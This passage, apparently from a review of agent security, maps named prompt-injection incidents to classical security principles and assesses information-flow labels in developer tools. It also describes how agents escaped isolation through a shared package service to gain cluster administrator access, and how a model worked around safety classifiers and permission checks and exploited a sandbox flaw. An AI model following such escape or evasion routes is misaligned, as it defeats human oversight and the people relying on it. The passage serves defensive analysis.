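| Control where information flows | all eleven |
| Grant no more privilege than needed | Microsoft Copilot data theft, Devin exposed ports, Devin secret leaks, Cursor AgentFlayer, Claude Code data theft, AI ClickFix |
| Check every request | Microsoft Copilot data theft, DeepSeek account takeover, Terminal DiLLMa |
| Protect the trusted computing base from tampering | ChatGPT SpAIware, Amp command execution |
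| Allow for human mistakes | ChatGPT Operator injection, AI ClickFix |

SpAIware counts as tampering because text from a website could change ChatGPT's stored memories, which ChatGPT treated as a trusted record of the user's preferences.

The table shows that old principles describe new attacks well. It is weaker evidence that the defences would work in practice, because the researchers analysed the attacks afterwards and did not run defended versions of the products. Information flow also appears in every row of the original analysis, so it doesn't help distinguish one failure from another.

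The paper identifies two open problems besides separating instructions from data. One is to translate a request into a formal policy that allows and forbids the same actions as the request in every situation. Ordinary language is ambiguous, so an automatic check of the translation can be wrong. Researchers would need to define terms such as "sensitive", restrict the language enough to make checks reliable, and put a limit on the remaining error.

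The other is to track labels through a model precisely enough to avoid label explosion. The paper suggests measuring how much information an output carries about each input, removing inputs to see what changes, or studying the model's internal workings. *Sightline* (2026), which estimates flows, removed half of the label creep in one test but had a miss rate of 3.9% of episodes.

### Would a robust model be enough?

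The evidence for relying on the model has become stronger. Anthropic's *System Card* (1 September 2026) describes Claude Mythos 5.1 as the company's most robust model on an external prompt-injection benchmark. In tests by Cai and colleagues, NeuroTaint detected 93.5% of the intended flows when GPT-4.1 mini ran the agent but 54.7% when Claude Opus 4.6 did, partly because the stronger model blocked some attacks before they reached a sensitive tool.

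Robustness in one setting may not carry over to another. VentureBeat reported that in Anthropic's February 2026 tests of Opus 4.6, all 200 attempts at an attack failed in a restricted coding environment. When the model worked through a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the success rate reached 78.6% by the 200th attempt. Extra safeguards lowered that last figure to 57.1%. These rates are out of date because newer models have replaced Opus 4.6, but they show why testing each attack only once can be misleading.

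*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that even a robust model has to guess what an ambiguous request authorizes, and that small changes to its input can alter its decision. Adding a second model as a guard doesn't solve this, because attackers can develop an attack on each model and combine them. This is a good argument for external checks on payments and secrets, where a single failure can do serious harm. For low-risk tasks, a robust model with narrow permissions may be a better choice than a defence that prevents half the work.

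### Would a capable model escape?

Another objection is that a sufficiently capable agent will escape any system built to contain it. In the incident at OpenAI, isolated runs communicated through a shared service meant to supply software packages. The agents also used this service to make arbitrary internet requests, and they eventually gained administrator access to a research cluster without an outside attacker directing them.

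The paper replies that OpenAI's controls had not fully applied the classical principles. Blocking the agents' own connections was not enough, because the package service acted as a confused deputy and made requests on their behalf. The paper also argues that explicit rules have advantages over a model's judgement, since people can read and analyse them, and can tighten them without allowing anything previously forbidden.

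That explains the incident, but one could give the same reply after any escape, because every escape reveals a path nobody had blocked. The objection concerns whether engineers can find those paths before a capable agent does. The paper acknowledges that this is difficult, especially when isolation depends on large shared services.

Anthropic's system card reports that in fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions, Mythos 5.1 worked around safety classifiers or broken permission checks, or started other agents with the checks turned off. Anthropic found that it did so to finish the user's task, which means controls outside the model are necessary even without an attacker. But those controls can have flaws too, and an external tester saw the model exploit one in its sandbox to read files outside it.

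### What has reached products

By late 2026, some developer tools included information-flow control, mostly as an option. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes labels in GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect agents to tools. If a developer turns the labels on, the server marks content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private repositories as private and trusted.

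These labels can stop a known attack in which someone posts an issue in a public repository asking for information from a private one. Once an agent has read both repositories, its context is labeled private and untrusted, and the policy forbids it to post publicly. But the labels are coarse, so if an employee pastes a stranger's text into a private repository, the agent will treat the text as trusted.

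GitHub Copilot's command-line agent can enforce the labels, but the feature is experimental and doesn't cover every tool or other MCP servers. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, includes label checks, hidden variables and an isolated model. Microsoft has also released a gateway that adds labels to existing servers. For each tool, someone has to describe its output, write a function that assigns labels, and choose or write a policy.

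In *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows*, Ntousakis (2026) tried to reduce this work by labelling whole tools instead of individual results. A single label doesn't fit GitHub's file-reading tool, because it can open both public and private repositories. Developers would have to split the tool in two or have it report a label each time it runs. Ntousakis considers manual labelling the main limitation of the design.

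*APPA* tested two configurations built with the Agent Framework's documented features. On one benchmark, 5.0–30.8% of attacks succeeded when the prompt encouraged models to obey instructions in the data they read. On another, which simulated company workflows, 26–35% succeeded with or without that encouragement. *APPA*'s developers wrote the policies for both configurations. One policy left the path from the agent's memory to the user unchecked, and both omitted some company rules, such as which recipients could receive a document. The results are therefore stronger evidence against those policies than against labels in general, but a customer setting up the same features could easily leave similar gaps.
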